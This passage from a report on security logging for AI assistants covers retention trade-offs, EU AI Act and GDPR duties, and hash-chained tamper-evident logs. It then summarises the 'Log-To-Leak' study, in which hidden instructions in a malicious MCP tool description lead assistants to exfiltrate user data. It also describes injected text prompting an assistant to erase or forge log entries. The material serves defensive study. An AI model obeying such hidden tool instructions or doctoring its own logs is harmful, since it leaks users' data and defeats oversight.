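Finally, the company can delete content sooner than metadata, for example content after 30 days and metadata after one year. This works for attacks it discovers quickly, but a planted memory, like those in *Trojan Hippo*, can still take effect after more than a month. By then, the log might identify the email that planted the memory but no longer contain its text. The company could reduce this loss by keeping flagged sessions in full. It could also keep the text of public web pages longer than employees' messages, because the pages are less private and an attacker may change them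 later.

Storage costs are a weak reason to delete metadata early. Sharif estimates that an entry takes up to 2,000 bytes. At 10,000 sessions a day and 28.5 calls per session (the average in Uber's benchmark), one entry per call would take up to about 210 gigabytes a year.

| Method | What an investigator can still do | What the investigator loses |
|---|---|---|
| Redaction at capture | Read the rest of the session | The removed text, permanently |
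| Hashes in place of text | Check whether a suspected copy matches | Any text that nobody has kept elsewhere |
| Separate store for content | Read everything once someone grants access | Time |
| Short retention for content | Read recent sessions, and follow the order of events in older ones | The hostile text and leaked data in older sessions |

#### Uber's choice

Uber keeps session content and protects it mainly through access rules. According to Li and colleagues, software scans the stored sessions and redacts passwords and other secrets where possible. Uber keeps the data for 13 months. Only security staff can see it, and each has only the access their job requires. The company's legal, privacy and risk teams reviewed the system before deployment.

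At 10,000 sessions a day, 13 months of data is about four million sessions. Keeping data that long helps with attacks that take months to surface, but a scan for secrets would leave most private remarks in place. The access rule stops managers from reading those remarks, but it doesn't stop a curious member of the security team or an intruder with that person's login. A company that makes the same choice should log every time someone opens a session and have a person outside the security team review those entries.

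### Logging duties under the EU AI Act

The EU's AI Act will require logs for systems it classes as high-risk. These include AI used in employment, education, credit assessment, law enforcement and critical infrastructure, according to the National Law Review. An assistant that ranks job applicants would probably count as high-risk, but one that only summarises suppliers' proposals probably wouldn't.

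The European Commission's *Article 12* requires high-risk systems to be able to record events automatically throughout their lifetime. The log must cover events that help identify risks and monitor how the system operates. The article prescribes no general format and doesn't specify whether the log must include the text of prompts. It lists minimum fields, such as the start and end of each use, only for remote biometric identification.

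The European Commission's *Article 26* requires an organisation that uses a high-risk system to keep the automatic logs under its control for at least six months. datenschutz notizen's *AI Logging under the EU AI Act* explains that the system's provider must also keep the logs it controls. Sharif wrongly attributes the six-month minimum to Article 12, and recommends keeping logs for 12 months for high-risk systems.

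Some vendors' default retention periods would be too short. OpenAI's compliance platform deletes logs after 30 days, and Microsoft's default of 180 days is slightly less than six months. A company that used either product for a high-risk purpose would probably need to export the logs or extend the retention period.

None of these duties applies yet. They were due to start on 2 August 2026, but *Regulation (EU) 2026/1744* (2026) postponed them shortly before that date. They now start on 2 December 2027 for the uses listed above, and on 2 August 2028 for AI in products already covered by EU safety rules, such as medical devices. Sharif's draft, dated 19 August 2026, still gives the old date.

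Systems already in use before the new dates will have to comply only if their design later changes significantly. Systems intended for public authorities have a separate deadline of 2 August 2030. Vendors often replace the models in their assistants, so whether an existing assistant has to comply may depend largely on whether a new model counts as a significant change.

### Data protection and monitoring employees

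The EU's General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR), by contrast, requires companies to collect only the personal data they need for a stated purpose (data minimisation) and to delete it when they no longer need it. The AI Act doesn't override these requirements. The Future of Life Institute's *Digital Omnibus on AI* (2026), which reproduces the amended text, includes a provision that data protection law applies to personal data handled under the Act. Article 26 also allows exceptions to the six-month minimum where data protection law requires them.

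A company therefore can't cite the AI Act as a reason to keep every prompt indefinitely. It could keep a basic record of events for six months or more and delete the content sooner, if the remaining record allows the monitoring that Article 12 requires. But it would need to justify both periods, because neither article specifies how much content is enough.

Article 26 requires employers to inform workers and their representatives before using a high-risk system at work. It also requires organisations to use the provider's information when they have to assess the system's effect on data protection. These rules concern the high-risk system itself, but security logs of an ordinary office assistant can also reveal a great deal about employees, and national laws may restrict such monitoring or require consultation first.

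The AI Act's high-risk uses include systems intended to monitor and evaluate workers' performance and behaviour. A detector for hijacked assistants has a different purpose, but it could fall into that category if managers began using it to score their staff. The company should therefore state in writing who may read the log and for what purposes, and rule out its use in performance reviews.

### Altered and forged entries

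If an assistant can write to its own log, an injected instruction may lead it to delete the evidence of the injection. Sharif allows agents to record their own actions in deployments that need little assurance. For deployments that need more, he recommends a separate recorder, such as a gateway, that uses its own secret key to sign each entry. The assistant should not be able to access that key or change stored entries.

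Hostile text can still produce false entries. In a plain-text log with one entry per line, a line break in a web page's text could create what looks like a second entry. A structured format prevents this if the software encodes line breaks, which keeps the page's text inside its own field. Sharif also requires software to check every entry against the format before accepting it.

Another kind of forgery passes that check. Suppose the assistant has a tool for adding notes to the log, and a hostile document leads it to write, falsely, that Maya approved a transfer. The recorder would sign the note like any other entry, so evidence of approval should come only from the software that showed Maya the question and received her answer.

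#### Append-only storage

Append-only storage accepts new entries but prevents anyone from changing or deleting old ones. An intruder who took over the recorder could add false entries but couldn't remove the earlier ones that show how the break-in began.

Sharif recommends keeping two copies of the log, one that staff search every day and one that is append-only. Someone other than the assistant's operator, such as a compliance team, should run the append-only copy so that one dishonest administrator can't alter both. Software compares the copies every hour or every day.

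#### A hash chain in three entries

A hash chain makes changes detectable, including in storage that permits them. Each entry contains a hash of the whole entry before it:

$$\text{previous hash}_n = \text{SHA-256}(\text{entry}_{n-1})$$

SHA-256 is a standard method for computing hashes. Its results are usually written as 64 characters, but the table uses invented four-character hashes for three events from Maya's session.

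| Entry | Event | Previous hash stored in the entry | Hash of this entry |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | The assistant finds the price file | None | 4f1a |
| 2 | A rule stops the assistant from sharing the file | 4f1a | 9c27 |
| 3 | The assistant emails the prices to an outsider | 9c27 | e803 |

The recorder builds the chain as follows:

1. It writes entry 1 and computes its hash, 4f1a.
2. It writes entry 2 with 4f1a inside it, then computes the hash of the whole entry, 9c27.
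3. It writes entry 3 with 9c27 inside it and computes its hash, e803.
4. It saves e803 in a separate place.

Software checks the chain by recomputing the hashes. If someone has changed entry 2 to record that the rule allowed the sharing, its hash will no longer match 9c27, the value in entry 3. Deleting entry 2 also causes a mismatch, because entry 3 would then follow entry 1, whose hash is 4f1a.

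Someone who can rewrite the whole log can repair these mismatches. After deleting entry 2, they could put 4f1a into entry 3 so that the two remaining entries form a valid chain. But the hash of entry 3 would no longer be e803, so the saved copy of that hash would expose the change. Without that copy, they could also alter or delete entry 3 unnoticed, since no later entry depends on it. Sharif therefore recommends saving a final hash for each session in a separate append-only system. Signatures add protection because the person would also need the recorder's key to sign the altered entries.

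The chain takes little computing time. Sharif puts the cost at about two milliseconds per signed entry.

#### What an intact chain can't prove

An intact chain, with its final hash stored safely, shows that the entries haven't changed since that hash was saved, but they could have been wrong when they were written. The false note about Maya's approval would pass this check, and so would an entry with the wrong time from a faulty clock.

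A hash chain also can't prove that the log is complete. In 2025, Copilot sometimes summarised files without recording that it had opened them. A hash chain over those logs would have passed every check, because the missing entries were never written. Sharif's format ends each session with a count of its entries, but that count includes only the entries the recorder wrote. To find omissions, a company has to compare the log with an independent one, such as the mail service's record of sent messages.

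#### Erasing personal data from a chain

People in the EU can ask a company to erase their personal data in some circumstances, but deleting an entry breaks the chain. Sharif proposes replacing the entry with a "tombstone" that records the reason for the deletion and the original entry's hash. In the example, a tombstone for entry 2 would contain 9c27, so checking software could still link it to entry 3.

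Tombstones create a new way to hide evidence. The hash in entry 3 covers the original entry but not the tombstone's text, so someone who can create tombstones could delete an incriminating entry and give a false reason. A second person should approve each tombstone.

Storing the content separately makes most erasures simpler. The chain can contain a keyed hash of each email or prompt, so the company can delete the text without changing the chain. It would still need tombstones for chain entries that themselves contain personal data, such as a name or an email address.

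### Log-To-Leak

Attackers can also disguise data theft as logging. *Log-To-Leak* (Hu, Fan and colleagues, 2026) tests a malicious MCP server that offers a logging tool. The user or their company has installed it alongside legitimate servers, such as GitHub's. Hidden instructions in one of its tool descriptions lead the assistant to call the logger after finishing the user's task. The call sends the attacker the user's request, the name of the last legitimate server used, that server's response and the assistant's answer.

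The researchers tried 555 requests on five legitimate servers, covering software development, maps, payments, market data and web browsing. They used GPT-4o, GPT-5, Claude Sonnet 4 and GPT-OSS-120B. GPT-5 couldn't make valid tool calls on two of the servers, which left 18 combinations of model and server.

In those combinations, the assistant made the extra call in 63 to 100% of runs. When it did, an average of 77 to 96% of the four pieces of information were accurate. How much the wording mattered depended on the model. With GPT-4o and GitHub, a simpler version of the hidden instructions succeeded in 38% of runs, compared with 63% for the full version. With Claude Sonnet 4, the simpler version succeeded in about 99% or more of runs on every server.

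Users would often have had little reason to complain, because the share of tasks completed changed by less than seven percentage points in 16 of the 18 combinations. The other two involved GPT-5, whose completion rate fell from 72% to 51% with GitHub and from 51% to 33% with the map service.

These models are older than the leading models at the end of 2026, and newer ones may behave differently. Hu and colleagues also reproduced the attack in two real products, Cursor with GPT-5.1 and Claude Desktop with Claude Sonnet 4.5, but tested only one configuration of each. They used their own logging tools and collected no outside users' data.

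#### The defences tested

Hu and colleagues tested three defences in full runs with GPT-4o and GitHub, where the attack had its lowest success rate.

| Defence | Runs in which the attack succeeded |
|---|---|
| None | 62.6% |
| Prompt sandwiching, which repeats the user's task after outside text | 59.6% |
| GPT-4o checks the tool descriptions first | 55.4% |
| IPIGuard, which plans tool calls according to how they depend on one another | 60.5% |

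All three also reduced the number of tasks the assistant completed, by about two to six percentage points.

Two other detectors only classified tool descriptions. DataSentinel classified all 100 malicious descriptions as safe. The second detector, which looks for instructions, flagged 91 of the malicious descriptions but also 136 of the 159 harmless ones. Legitimate descriptions often tell a model when and how to use a tool, so instructions are weak evidence that a description is malicious.

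Hu and colleagues suggest checking the call instead. The assistant's software could require separate approval before it sends one server's data to another or makes a call that the user's task doesn't need. They did not test these controls.

#### The trace it leaves

A successful attack adds one tool call after the last call the task needed. This call sends the user's request and another server's response to the malicious server, which a reviewer could see if the log included full arguments. If the log included only tool names, the call would look like routine logging, and the reviewer might ignore it or even exempt it from alerts.

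A company can make this call stand out by giving the model no logging tools. The software around the model should write the log anyway, so any call from the model to a logger would deserve an alert. Because an attacker could give the tool another name, the company should also look for calls that copy one server's response to another server. Some of these calls will be legitimate, such as when a user asks the assistant to save search results in a notes app, so the check also needs the user's request as input.
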